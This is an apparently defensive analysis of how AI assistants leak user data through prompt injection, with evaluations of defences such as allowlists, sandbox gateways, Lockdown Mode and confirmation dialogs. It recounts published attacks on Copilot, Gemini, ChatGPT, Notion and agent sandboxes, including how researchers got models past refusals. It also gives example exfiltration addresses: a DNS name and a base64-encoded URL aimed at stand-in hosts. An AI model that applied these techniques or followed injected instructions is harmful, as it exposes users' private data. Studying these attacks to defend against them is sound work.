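### Refusing links found inside fetched pages

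Anthropic's fix has a much larger effect, because it prevents a website from adding addresses as it receives more data. Claude can then choose only among addresses from the user or from search results. An attacker whose pages appear several times in the search results can still use that choice to leak data, but can't add to the list between fetches unless Claude searches again.

The fix makes it hard for Claude to read anything that spans several pages, so dyb suggests, as a compromise, letting it follow links only on domains the user has named in the conversation. This would restore most ordinary browsing, but it wouldn't help a user who asked Claude to look at the coffee shop's website without giving its domain.

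A public index limits the same attack without banning links. Paul's site would have needed 20,439 indexed pages to let Claude spell any three characters, and more than 550,000 for any four. A crawler might well stop before indexing all of a site that large. The index therefore blocks leaks of long names but still allows leaks of short answers.

Another suggestion from dyb is to watch for a run of requests to one site in which each address is one character longer than the last. This would have caught Paul's attack, but an attacker could instead assign whole words to the links, and the resulting addresses would look much like those of an ordinary website.

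Liang and colleagues propose instead that the assistant download a fixed number of pages for every question and then choose among the copies. The attacker's server receives no record of that choice. In their tests, this lowered the score for recovering questions from 0.89 to 0.39, without any extra work for the model. The assistant presumably has to download pages it won't use, and a fixed number may be too small for a difficult question.

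### Limits on the number of fetches

A cap on fetches reduces k in the formula directly. This table shows how many fetches different secrets need if the attacker knows the order and repeats are allowed:

| Secret | Bits | Fetches with 36 addresses | Fetches with 1,000 addresses |
|---|---|---|---|
| Whether the user has a certain illness | 1 | 1 | 1 |
| Four-digit PIN | 13.3 | 3 | 2 |
| Six-digit login code | 19.9 | 4 | 2 |
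| Ten-digit telephone number | 33.2 | 7 | 4 |
| Random 128-bit key | 128 | 25 | 13 |
| 1,000 letters and digits of text | About 5,170 | 1,000 | 519 |

A cap of 20 fetches would protect the full text, and it would protect the key against an attacker with 36 addresses. The model could still leak a summary of the text in a few words, though. An assistant could answer most everyday questions within that limit, but a research agent that reads dozens of websites couldn't do its job.

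No practical cap on fetches protects short secrets. In Willison's example, a developer limits Claude's web fetch tool to five fetches. If the first loads the attacker's page, the remaining four are enough to leak a login code. A cap of four would leave only three, which would narrow the code to about 21 possibilities if the attacker has 36 addresses to choose from each time. A website that allows five guesses would let the attacker in nearly a quarter of the time. An attack that persists in the assistant's memory, as ZombieAgent did, can collect the rest of the secret in the next conversation, unless the secret has expired.

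## Requests made by servers, code sandboxes and messaging apps

A content security policy covers only the requests that the browser makes for the chat page, and a check on addresses or a cap on fetches covers only the requests that pass through it. An assistant can cause requests in several other ways.

Four kinds of software commonly send such requests, and each needs its own restriction:

| What sends the request | Where it usually runs | What can restrict it |
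|---|---|---|
| The assistant's fetch or search tool | The vendor's servers | A check on the address, such as URL anchoring, or a list of permitted hosts |
| Code that the assistant runs in a sandbox | The vendor's servers or the user's computer | A gateway outside the sandbox that permits only listed hosts |
| A messaging app that previews links | The messaging company's servers | Switching previews off |
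| A mail program that displays the assistant's messages | The user's device | Removing external images from the messages |

### Fetch tools that open composed addresses

Varonis' *Reprompt* describes an attack on Copilot Personal, the consumer version of Microsoft's assistant. As in the later SearchLeak attack, the victim clicked a link that led to a Microsoft site and contained the attacker's prompt. The prompt made Copilot's fetch tool open an address containing the victim's data.

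Microsoft had two safeguards against this. Copilot usually refused to open an address without a good reason, and it could remove sensitive data from an address before opening it. The researchers got past the first safeguard by presenting the request as a puzzle. The second failed because Microsoft had assumed that checking the first request was enough. In one test, Copilot removed a secret phrase from the address on its first attempt but sent the phrase intact when it repeated the task. Varonis thinks Microsoft probably skipped the later checks to keep Copilot fast.

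Each page the attacker's server returned then contained instructions for what Copilot should send next, such as the user's location or a summary of their last conversation. Nobody could tell from the original link what the attacker would ask for, and security software on the victim's device couldn't see the later instructions. The leak continued even if the victim closed the Copilot tab. The attack became public in January 2026, and *Microsoft Copilot Reprompt Attack Enables Stealthy Data Exfiltration* (Underhill, 2026) reports that Microsoft had patched the vulnerability. Microsoft 365 Copilot was not affected.

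By then the same researchers had reported a second attack on Copilot Personal. Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) explains how one click could leak data from the services a user had connected, including Gmail, Google Drive and Google Calendar. In a test, Copilot found an email containing a password. It could encode what it found, put it in a URL and ask its fetch tool to summarise the page at that address. Microsoft had assumed that only the user would start a search of the connected services, but an undocumented setting in the link ran the attacker's prompt as soon as the page loaded. The researchers had learned of the setting from Copilot's explanation of why such an attack was supposedly impossible.

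Varonis reported CoSnitch in December 2025, and Microsoft released the patches on 18 August 2026. TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot* gives CoSnitch's identifier as CVE-2026-24301. Varonis knew of no real attacks that used it.

Varonis points out that a network monitor would detect nothing unusual in CoSnitch, because Copilot routinely fetches web pages. But URL anchoring with an exact match would have stopped both this attack and Reprompt, because the completed address didn't appear in the attacker's prompt, which counted as the user's message.

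Google's Gemini had a similar gap in its tool for reading web pages. Tenable's *The Trifecta* (2025) reports that Gemini at first flagged a request to send out the user's saved information as odd and refused it. However, a feature that displays Gemini's reasoning also showed how it called the browsing tool. When the researchers wrote their request in the same form, Gemini opened a web address containing the user's saved information.

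Google had protected the display of the answer because it assumed data would leave there. It has since fixed the flaw. Tenable reports that Google now prevents this kind of leak through browsing when the instructions come from an indirect injection, but doesn't explain how.

### Search tools that accept an address

Attackers can exploit a search tool as they would a fetch tool, even though a search tool should send words to a search engine, not a request to a site the attacker chooses. Notion, which makes software for notes and company documents, gave its AI agents a search tool in version 3.0, released in September 2025. In *The Hidden Risk in Notion 3.0 AI Agents*, Willison describes how Abi Raghuram hid instructions in a PDF that made the agent collect a company's client data, put it into a web address and pass that address to the search tool as its query.

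The Decoder's *Notion AI agents get security update after potential data leak* (2025) attributes the research to the security company CodeIntegrity and explains that the tool could also fetch external URLs. The victim only had to upload the PDF, which looked like a customer feedback report, and ask for a summary. Notion's designers evidently paid too little attention to what counts as a search query.

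Notion responded quickly by improving its detection of injections and asking users for approval before an agent opened a suspicious link or one the model had generated. The rule about generated links is close to URL anchoring. Administrators can also switch off the agents' web access.

Claude Sonnet 4, the model in CodeIntegrity's demonstration, did very well in a larger test of the same weakness. For that test, Rall, Bauer and colleagues (2025), in *Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration*, built an agent that could search a company's documents and retrieve web pages. Hidden text in a blog post instructed the agent to look up a secret and send it out with the same web tool that had fetched the post. They used 12 versions of each of 89 attack texts, counting the original, for a total of 1,068 attacks per model.

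Grok 4 leaked the secret in 72.4% of the attacks, whereas Claude Sonnet 4 and several other models never did. Model size made no clear difference. But the researchers ran each attack only once, and many of the attack texts came from well-known collections. Notion's agent, running Claude Sonnet 4, leaked data when someone wrote instructions tailored to the product. A score of zero on a fixed set of attacks is therefore weak evidence that a fetch tool can safely open any address the model requests.

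### An experiment that compared prompts with an allowlist

Lan, Kaul and colleagues at eBay measured how well several defences protect a fetch tool in *Silent Egress* (2026). They built a small agent that automatically previewed any link the user mentioned. The user always asked the agent to summarise a page, and the agent's input also contained a secret. The page contained hidden instructions to send the secret to the attacker's server.

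The researchers varied three things:

- They put the instructions in the page's title, its description, its main text or the text of a link.
- They led the agent to the page directly or through redirects.
- They asked for the whole secret in one request or for four fragments in separate requests.

Each of the 16 combinations was run 30 times. The agent contacted the attacker's server in 423 of the 480 runs, or 88.1%. It did so in 238 of 240 runs when the instructions asked for a single request, but in 185 of 240 when it had to split the secret. In 95% of the successful attacks, the summary the user received gave no sign of the leak. In 120 runs with harmless pages, the agent never contacted the attacker's server.

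They then chose the simplest version, with the instructions in the main text, and added one defence at a time:

| Defence | Runs in which the agent tried to leak data | Runs in which it succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| None | 30 of 30 | 30 |
| A standing instruction to treat web content as data | 20 of 30 | 20 |
| Markers around web content | 30 of 30 | 30 |
| Both | 17 of 30 | 17 |
| Domain allowlist | 30 of 30 | 0 |
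| Filter for suspicious-looking addresses | 25 of 30 | 0 |
| Filter for words such as "password" | 7 of 30 | 0 |
| Filter for random-looking text | 0 of 30 | 0 |

The allowlist contained four domains, none of them the attacker's. The model tried to send the secret in every trial, and the software blocked every attempt. An allowlist is a deterministic defence, so the result would be the same for any model. For the same reason, the experiment shows little about how allowlists fail. Lan and colleagues chose an attacker's domain that no sensible list would include, and they acknowledge that a real attacker could use an open redirect or a compromised site on the list.

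The results for the filters are harder to interpret. Lan and colleagues call the filter for suspicious addresses "redirect detection", but it blocks certain patterns. One of these is the word "collect" in the path, which their own attack used. The two filters in the last rows should act only after the model has written an address, yet the model made far fewer attempts when they were on. The researchers suggest that the model avoided or disguised the blocked text, but they don't say they told it about the filters.

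The prompt-level results depend on the model. The researchers tested only Qwen2.5 7B, a small model that was already old in 2026, and gave it a minimal standing prompt with the secret in plain view. The 17 leaks in 30 runs are compatible with a true rate of about 37% to 75%, so the two prompt defences together may have worked no better than the instruction alone. The attacks were also simple and didn't adapt to the defences. A stronger model might resist all of them, as Claude Sonnet 4 did in Rall's test, and a more determined attacker might succeed more often. Lan and colleagues argue that better models could be more vulnerable because they follow instructions more reliably, but this wouldn't explain the large differences between models that Rall and colleagues found.

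### A gateway for code sandboxes

Many assistants can write and run programs, for example to analyse a spreadsheet. They run these programs in a sandbox, a closed-off environment with its own files. A program in a sandbox can contact servers without using the assistant's fetch tool, so checks inside that tool don't apply. The program can also start other programs that make their own connections.

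The usual control is a gateway, typically a proxy that handles all traffic leaving the sandbox:

1. A firewall blocks every connection from the sandbox except those to the gateway.
2. A program that wants to reach a server gives the gateway the server's host name.
3. The gateway looks for the name on its allowlist. It either makes the connection or returns an error.
4. If the server replies with a redirect to another host, the program has to request a new connection, and the gateway checks that name too.

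The fourth step treats redirects much as a content security policy does, by checking each new host.

*Permission Denied* (2026) uses a gateway of this kind to test programming agents under strict security rules. The gateway's allowlist has 205 domains, adapted from the default list for the web version of Claude Code. A request to any other domain returns a plain "403 Forbidden" error, and any attempt to bypass the proxy fails with a refused connection.

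Claude Code has a sandbox in which, according to Anthropic, programs can reach the internet only through a proxy. The proxy runs outside the sandbox, since hostile code might tamper with one inside it. Claude Code asks the user when a program requests a new domain, but administrators can have it block new domains without asking.

OpenAI offers similar controls for Codex. In the cloud version, *Agent internet access* lets developers turn the internet off or choose a list of allowed sites. One ready-made list covers the sites programmers commonly need to download software. On the user's own computer, OpenAI keeps network access off by default, and the optional rules about which destinations Codex can reach also cover any programs that a command starts.

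Developers can also limit Codex in the cloud to requests that normally only retrieve information. This should stop most uploads, such as the one that sent files to a permitted Anthropic address in the Claude Cowork attack. But a program can still put data in the address of one of these requests, and Google Forms can store data sent this way.

Gateways usually compare host names because the numerical (IP) addresses behind them change. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* (2026), which sets out a design for running agents on company servers, calls rules based on IP addresses insufficient for this reason. Sandboxes in its design typically have no external access. When a task needs external access, a proxy inspects the traffic and the request triggers an approval.

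A company that runs an agent on its own network has a second reason to restrict the agent's requests. *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (2026) warns that attackers can use such an agent to reach internal systems that outsiders can't contact, including administrative pages and the services that give cloud servers their settings. The paper recommends blocking internal addresses unless the agent clearly needs them.

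Most gateways don't inspect the contents of the traffic they let through. Anthropic has warned Claude Code users that domain fronting may get past the proxy. An encrypted connection names the host twice, once openly during setup and once inside the encryption. Some large hosting networks serve many customers' sites from the same machines, so a program can show the proxy a permitted name and then request the attacker's site inside the encrypted part.

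Docker, which makes software for running programs in isolated containers, gives almost the same warning about its own agent sandboxes and calls the problem inherent to proxying encrypted traffic. A proxy that decrypts the traffic could compare the two names, but it could also read every password the sandbox sends.

### Name lookups as a side channel

A sandbox can leak data even when its firewall blocks every connection. Before a program can contact a server, it has to look up the server's IP address in the domain name system (DNS), and the lookup can carry data.

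Suppose a program in the sandbox looks up `clinic-tuesday-0900.pictures.example`. The sandbox's name server has no record of that name, so the query is forwarded until it reaches the name server responsible for `pictures.example`. The attacker runs that server and logs the full name, including the appointment. A firewall that blocks only connections doesn't stop this leak, because the program never connects to `pictures.example`.

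Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) reports that the sandbox where ChatGPT runs code could leak data through DNS lookups. OpenAI had blocked direct connections, assuming this cut the sandbox off from the internet, but lookups still worked. An attacker could exploit this with a prompt that promised to unlock paid features, or with a custom version of ChatGPT.

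The researchers built one that posed as a personal doctor. When a user uploaded laboratory results, it sent the patient's name and the model's medical assessment to the researchers' server. ChatGPT told the user that the data hadn't gone anywhere, and didn't show the approval request that normally appears before it sends data to another company. OpenAI had already found the underlying problem itself, and it finished the fix on 20 February 2026.

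Amazon's cloud division, AWS, took longer to deal with the same fault. It had advertised one setting of AgentCore Code Interpreter, a sandbox it sells for other companies' agents, as providing "complete isolation with no external access". The security company BeyondTrust (2026) found that the sandbox could still send DNS lookups under that setting. Each lookup could carry up to 60 characters of encoded data, or 45 characters of ordinary text, so a password would fit in one lookup and a one-megabyte file would take about 22,000. BeyondTrust also hid commands in the IP addresses that its name server returned, which let it control the sandbox from outside.

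AWS received the report on 1 September 2025 and deployed a fix two months later, but withdrew it. In December, AWS decided to change its documentation instead. It explained that the sandbox needed lookups to reach Amazon's own storage service, and recommended another setting to customers who wanted full control. BeyondTrust published its findings on 16 March 2026, and AWS closed the route in mid-April.

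A gateway can prevent these leaks if programs in the sandbox send it host names instead of looking up any themselves. The gateway checks each name against the allowlist before looking it up, so a name under `pictures.example` never reaches the attacker. The design in *Containing the Autonomous Operator* permits lookups through the cluster's own name server, so data can still leak through them unless that server also refuses names that aren't on the allowlist. Lan and colleagues didn't test lookups, so their result for the allowlist doesn't cover them.

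### A helper outside the sandbox

The sandbox in Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, an agent for office work, blocked network access but leaked data through a service outside it. (The product is separate from Anthropic's Claude Cowork.) The sandbox used this service to exchange files with the user's storage. The service accepted a file's address and fetched the file.

PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Controlled by Attacker, Bypassing Sandbox* shows that code inside the sandbox could give this service any address. Microsoft had evidently assumed that the service would receive only the addresses of files in Microsoft's own storage. In the test, a user added a "skill", a package of instructions and scripts, found online. One of its scripts used the service to fetch a file from the attacker's server. The file contained commands, and the script sent their results back by including them in another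 address it requested.

The attacker could use this connection to read the victim's Outlook mail, SharePoint files and chat history. The connection still worked after the user pressed the stop button, because background programs kept running. PromptArmor reported the flaw on 24 June 2026, and Microsoft confirmed on 19 August that it had addressed the flaw.

The file service worked as a relay, like the Teams service in EchoLeak. A service that only moves files to and from Microsoft's storage needs a very short allowlist, so this gap was easier to close than the one in a general fetch tool.

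### Switching off link previews

A gateway doesn't help when a permitted messaging service sends the request. If an agent talks to its user through Telegram, the gateway has to let those messages through, and Telegram's server then requests any link in them to create a preview.

PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* found that OpenClaw, an agent that people can use through messaging apps, was exposed in this way with its default Telegram settings. The company set up a test site that records preview requests, so users can have their agent send a link to it and see what arrives. The site also shows which messaging apps' preview programs visit it most often.

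Users can stop the previews by setting `linkPreview` to `false` in the Telegram section of OpenClaw's configuration file. When PromptArmor repeated the test with this setting, the site received no data. The setting also removes thumbnails and descriptions. This matters little for an agent's answers, but the same agent may also post in a group where people like to see them, so PromptArmor would like messaging apps to offer a setting for each chat or channel.

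The messaging company has to provide a setting that turns link previews off, and the agent's developer has to use it, so both can easily overlook the problem. The safer default is for the agent to turn previews off in every message it sends, because the developer knows that a model wrote the links, while the messaging company may not know this.

### Messages to the user's own inbox

Copilot Cowork also leaked data through emails and Teams messages. Microsoft's documentation said that the agent asked for permission before sending either, but it skipped this step when the recipient was the user, presumably because Microsoft assumed that such messages were safe. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* explains that these messages could still leak data because they could contain external images, which Teams or Outlook requested from the attacker's server when the user opened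 the message.

The addresses of those images contained download links for the user's files. Copilot Cowork can create links that let anyone download a file without logging in, so one short address could expose a whole document. The instructions were five lines of an 81-line skill file. When the user asked for a review of the week's work, the agent sent a message with the hidden images. Its record of completed steps did not show the message's contents.

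The attack worked in all five of PromptArmor's trials. With so few trials, the true success rate could plausibly be as low as about 55%, but that would still be high enough to be useful to an attacker. The attack also worked with Claude Opus 4.7, the more advanced of the two models Copilot Cowork chose between. Opus leaked more files than the automatic setting did because it searched more thoroughly for recent documents. A user could also schedule the weekly review to run unattended, and the agent would then send a new message each time.

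Willison (2026), in *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, calls preventing exfiltration the biggest continuing challenge in designing such agents. The leak here came from connecting parts that each worked as their designers intended. Outlook displays images in emails, SharePoint creates download links, and a reminder to oneself hardly seems to need approval.

PromptArmor advises administrators to reduce the number of files each user can reach and to block downloads from sensitive SharePoint sites. Blocking downloads makes the files much harder to use, since people can then view them only in a browser and can't print them or open them in Word. The images would also remain, so an attacker could still put text from an email in an image's address.

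Microsoft could close that route by removing external images from every message the agent writes, as it already tries to do in Copilot's chat answers. Mail programs that block external images until the reader asks for them also offer some protection, but readers are likely to load images from a sender they trust, and here the sender is their own assistant. A message without images could still contain a link that leaks data if the reader clicks it.

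## Asking the user, and modes that cut off the network

A link leaks nothing until someone clicks it, so a vendor has more options for a suspicious link than for a suspicious image. It can remove the link, show the address as plain text, or keep the link and ask the user before opening it.

Removing the link protects the data but can make the answer less useful. Park (2024), in *Copilot*, describes answers in which Microsoft Copilot replaced a link with the notice "An external link was removed to protect your privacy". In Park's example, Copilot recommended further reading, but the notice replaced the source. Gemini and Salesforce's agents leave similar notices. Showing the address as plain text lets the user keep it, but pasting it into a browser sends the same request as clicking the link. Asking the user preserves the link but relies on the user to notice the leak.

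### Links with invisible text

A content security policy doesn't stop clicks on links, and in early 2024 Rehberger used a link to get data out of Microsoft 365 Copilot. Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot* (2024) describes an attack that began with hidden instructions in an email or a shared document. When the user asked about that email or document, Copilot searched, without asking permission, for other messages, including one with a login code for the chat service Slack. It then wrote a link to Rehberger's server, with the text of the message hidden in the address.

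The attack relied on Unicode, the standard that assigns a number to every character. Unicode includes a set of "tag" characters that mirror ordinary letters, digits and punctuation but are invisible in most software. In hexadecimal, the letter "c" is 63 and its tag version is E0063. A link could therefore appear as `https://bistro.example/` but contain a whole email, written in tag characters, after the final slash. When a browser requests such an address, it writes each tag character as 12 ordinary ones, so the 19 characters of "clinic-tuesday-0900" would reach the server as 228, which the attacker can easily convert back.

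Microsoft had assumed that people could see what a link contained before clicking it. Rehberger notes that hovering over the link shows that something is wrong, but a reader has little reason to check an address that already looks short and complete.

Microsoft closed Rehberger's first report, which covered only the invisible tag characters, as low severity. It opened a case in February 2024 after he demonstrated the whole attack by stealing sales figures. By July the attack no longer worked, and Rehberger made it public in August. Microsoft didn't explain the fix, but Copilot had apparently stopped displaying links. Rehberger had recommended that change, and also that Copilot ignore the tag characters and stop calling tools automatically. Ignoring the tag characters alone would not have been enough, because an attacker could have encoded the data in base64 instead.

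Copilot later had a similar problem with diagrams, which it could draw from a text notation called Mermaid. daily.dev's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Arbitrary Data Exfiltration via Mermaid Diagrams* summarises an attack by the researcher Adam Logue, who hid instructions in an Excel document. Copilot collected recent emails, encoded them and put them in a link behind a fake login button in a diagram. According to Red Hot Cyber, the victim would click the button believing it gave access to the document's sensitive content. An attacker who controls the answer can write both the link and the reason for clicking it. By September 2025, Microsoft had removed clickable links from the diagrams to fix this.

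### ChatGPT's confirmation dialog

ChatGPT displays links but asks the user to confirm some of them. OpenAI's help page *ChatGPT generated links* gives a harmless example. A user asks where to buy a car nearby. ChatGPT has information that the user lives in London, so it offers a car-search link ending in "London". Clicking the link produces useful results and also reveals to the car site where the user lives.

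OpenAI uses its scans of public websites to decide when to ask, as Safe Url does for automatic fetches. If a site's owner has asked OpenAI not to catalogue it, ChatGPT asks the user to confirm every link to that site. Users may therefore see the dialog even for ordinary articles from a newspaper that blocks OpenAI's crawler.

The dialog, titled "Check this link is safe", warns that the link is unverified and may share data from the conversation with another site. It shows the address and lets the user copy or open it. The help page advises users to look at the website and make sure they trust it. If something looks wrong, OpenAI suggests avoiding the link and asking ChatGPT for another source or a summary.

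### What a user can judge from an address

Suppose the dialog shows one of these addresses:

```
https://bistro.example/menu?ref=q7RfT2mVx0LbKc9ZsWn4EyHdUa
https://bistro.example/menu?ref=Y2xpbmljLXR1ZXNkYXktMDkwMA
```

The first ends in random characters, like the tracking codes that many newsletters and shops add to their links. The second ends in the base64 encoding of "clinic-tuesday-0900". Few people could tell them apart, and someone who refused all such addresses would refuse many legitimate ones.

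Checking the site's name works better when the attacker uses an unfamiliar domain. It doesn't help with a Google Form on `docs.google.com`, and it would not have helped against SearchLeak, an attack that required the victim to click a link to a genuine Microsoft site. *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Could Allow Data Theft Through a Link Click*, from Thailand's computer emergency team, ThaiCERT, notes that even phishing filters may struggle to detect such a link.

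Nor would the dialog reveal a leak through the choice of address, as with the weekday menus, because `https://bistro.example/tuesday` contains nothing private.

Users could judge a request more easily if the dialog showed the data and not only an address. According to Check Point Research, ChatGPT's approval request for GPT Actions, which connect custom versions of ChatGPT to other companies' services, shows both the destination and the data to be sent. For links, software could decode base64 before showing the address, but an attacker could have the model use a less common encoding.

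### How often people refuse

The best available evidence on approval requests comes from a study of coding commands, not links. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports an experiment with 1,053 paid professional testers. A research vendor hired them for a coding study and didn't tell them which behaviour it was measuring. Partway through each session, one permission request showed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one. The dangerous command never ran, even if the tester approved it. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it.

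Refusals fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more requests. This is consistent with ordinary use of Claude Code, where people approve 97% of permission requests. Most of those requests are probably harmless, so the high approval rate alone isn't evidence of carelessness, but the experiment suggests that many people have stopped reading the requests.

Anthropic ran the study to compare human approval with auto mode, in which a classifier reviews each action. The classifier blocked 937 of the 1,053 commands, or 89%. It blocked 800 that a tester had approved and missed only six that a tester had refused. Another 110 got past both the tester and the classifier.

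Anthropic was making the case for auto mode, and the testers might have been less careful than real users because they weren't working on their own projects. On the other hand, the planted command was clearly dangerous, while an address that leaks data usually looks harmless. ChatGPT's dialog probably appears less often than Claude Code's requests did, which should help people pay attention. But even early in a session, about five in six testers approved the dangerous command.

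People do seem to read some requests. Users reject 39% of the plans that Claude Code presents for approval, though perhaps often for reasons unrelated to safety. Those plans are written in plain language, and a link dialog could be too, for example by stating that the link would reveal a clinic appointment to a restaurant. But a model would probably have to write that sentence, and the hidden instructions might control what it wrote.

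Willison accepts that auto mode is better than constant approval requests, but points out that it still let 11% of the dangerous commands through. Anthropic announced on 22 October 2026 that auto mode would become the default in most Claude apps on its Pro, Max and Team plans. Its classifier is designed never to approve data exfiltration, so a user who wants such an action has to leave auto mode or run the command themselves. Anthropic says this reduces the risk but doesn't eliminate it, because a classifier can make mistakes.

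### What Lockdown Mode switches off

Lockdown Mode, an optional setting in ChatGPT, takes many of these decisions away from the user by limiting the features that could send data out. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced it on 13 February for organisations on four plans, including Enterprise and Edu. On 4 June, OpenAI began offering it to personal accounts and to businesses that manage their own subscriptions.

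OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, the current help page, lists what changes:

| Feature | In Lockdown Mode |
|---|---|
| Web browsing | Uses only cached pages |
| Images from the web | ChatGPT may not retrieve them or show images in ordinary answers |
| Deep Research and agent mode | Off |
| Code from Canvas, ChatGPT's editor | Can't use the network, even if the user would approve |
| File downloads for data analysis | Off, but users can still upload files |
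| Apps on personal accounts | No live access or changes to outside services where these conflict with the mode's protections |
| Apps in managed workspaces | The administrator decides |
| Memory, uploads, shared conversations and image generation | No change |
| Codex's network access | No change |

Suppose the user in the restaurant example has Lockdown Mode on. ChatGPT may still read the hidden paragraph in a cached copy of the review page, and the model may try to open the menu for Tuesday. But the request goes only to OpenAI's cache, so the attacker's server receives nothing. Cached browsing therefore also blocks leaks that depend on which address the model chooses, which URL anchoring alone can't block. However, search results may be old or missing because they come from the cache, and the hidden paragraph can still make the recommendation worse.

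Apps are the largest remaining gap in managed workspaces, because Lockdown Mode doesn't automatically turn them off there. OpenAI advises administrators not to enable any actions in apps they don't trust, and not to let trusted apps write anything that an outsider might see. For example, a comment on a document shared with a supplier could pass data to that supplier without using a web address. OpenAI classes other app actions as medium risk, and its list has no low-risk category. Reading from a trusted app, for instance, is medium risk because it can bring sensitive data into the conversation.

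The list of restrictions doesn't include links that the user clicks, so these presumably still depend on the confirmation dialog. Users with personal accounts can also turn the mode off for a single chat. Hidden instructions could make ChatGPT recommend this. Search results in Lockdown Mode may well be out of date, and ChatGPT could give that as the reason.

The Decoder's *ChatGPT's new Lockdown Mode lets you disable web access and more* quotes an earlier version of OpenAI's help page, which said that prompt injection "is not currently a major risk" but could grow. The current page instead calls prompt injection a known security risk. It still says that Lockdown Mode isn't intended for everyone and can't guarantee that no data will leak.

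### The preview that bypassed it

For part of 2026, a feature missing from OpenAI's list let data out of Lockdown Mode. The feature, HTML previews, displays web code as a live page inside a ChatGPT chat. Brinsa (2026), in *ChatGPT Locked the Doors and Left a Window Open*, points out that the previews arrived in February, the same month OpenAI announced the mode.

OpenAI ran the previews in a sandbox that asked for the user's approval before contacting an outside server, according to TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment*. It had also replaced the browser's function for opening new windows with one that asked for approval first, and assumed every popup would go through the replacement. Researchers at Check Point found a way to reach the original function. The sandbox's permissions then let the popup escape the sandbox's restrictions, The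 Hacker News reports.

In ChatGPT's desktop app, this needed no click. The researchers built a custom version of ChatGPT that sent the victim's messages to their server during a normal conversation. In a browser, the victim first had to click inside the preview, because browsers usually block popups the user didn't request. OpenAI fixed the flaw on 18 September 2026.

Even a careful user couldn't have refused the zero-click version, because no approval request appeared. Switching off a listed feature is a deterministic defence, but OpenAI also has to find every other feature that can open a connection, including those it adds later. Its help page still doesn't list HTML previews among the mode's restrictions.

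### Web search controls in Microsoft 365 Copilot

Administrators can switch off web searches in Microsoft 365 Copilot for particular users or groups. Parekh (2025) explains in *Microsoft 365 Copilot Web Search* that when searches are on, Copilot normally turns the user's prompt into a query of a few words and sends it to Bing. Copilot removes anything that identifies the user or the company and leaves out uploaded files. Microsoft logs every query so administrators can check it later.

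Microsoft's *Manage web searches in Copilot separately from optional connected experiences* describes three settings for web search: on everywhere, off everywhere, or off only in Work mode, where Copilot uses the company's own data. The last option lets employees look things up in Web mode while keeping web results away from internal documents, but an email can still bring hostile text into Work mode. If an administrator configures neither this policy nor an older one for online features, web search is on.

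Users can turn web content off for themselves when their administrator permits web search. In July 2026, Microsoft announced that this setting would cover more versions of Copilot.

Administrators can also make the restriction depend on what the user types. Microsoft (2026) describes a check for sensitive data in a prompt before Copilot searches the web. If the check finds any, Copilot can still use the company's internal content but can't send a query to Bing, according to Office 365 for IT Pros' *DLP Extends Its Ability to Control Copilot Processing*. Administrators have to configure this protection themselves. The check examines prompts, so it may miss private data that Copilot takes from an email while following hidden instructions.

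A commenter from a large healthcare organisation objected to Parekh's account because even an anonymous query reveals something about the prompt. The concern is fair for a hospital, but the data goes to Microsoft under contract, not to an attacker.

These settings are narrower than Lockdown Mode. EchoLeak and SearchLeak sent data out through images that the user's browser loaded, so switching off web search probably would not have stopped either.

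### The dispute over ChatGPT's default settings

In *OpenAI Help*, Willison (2026) welcomed Lockdown Mode for its deterministic limits, but inferred from its existence that ChatGPT's default settings don't provide robust protection against a determined attacker. Dane Stuckey, OpenAI's head of security, considered the lost features a worthwhile trade-off for people at higher risk because of who they are, what they work on or what data they handle.

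The mode's existence is weak evidence by itself, because a company can offer a stricter setting even if its ordinary one is adequate. OpenAI's announcement supports Willison more directly. It says the mode disables some features entirely because OpenAI can't give "strong deterministic guarantees of data safety" for them, but people who leave the mode off can still use them. OpenAI also labeled some network features "Elevated Risk", explaining that the industry's safeguards don't yet fully address their risks.

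Stuckey and Willison therefore don't really disagree about how ChatGPT works. It's unclear how much the remaining risk matters to ordinary users. In February, OpenAI said that most people didn't need the mode, but that executives and security teams at prominent organisations, for example, might. They are obvious targets, but hidden instructions on a popular web page can reach anyone, and ordinary users also have medical letters and login codes. OpenAI's announcement and help page include no figures for attacks on either group.

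Someone with a personal account could leave Lockdown Mode on and turn it off only for chats that need the live web. This would keep most of the protection. But Lockdown Mode doesn't change ChatGPT's memory, so a chat with the mode off may have access to private details the user mentioned while it was on.
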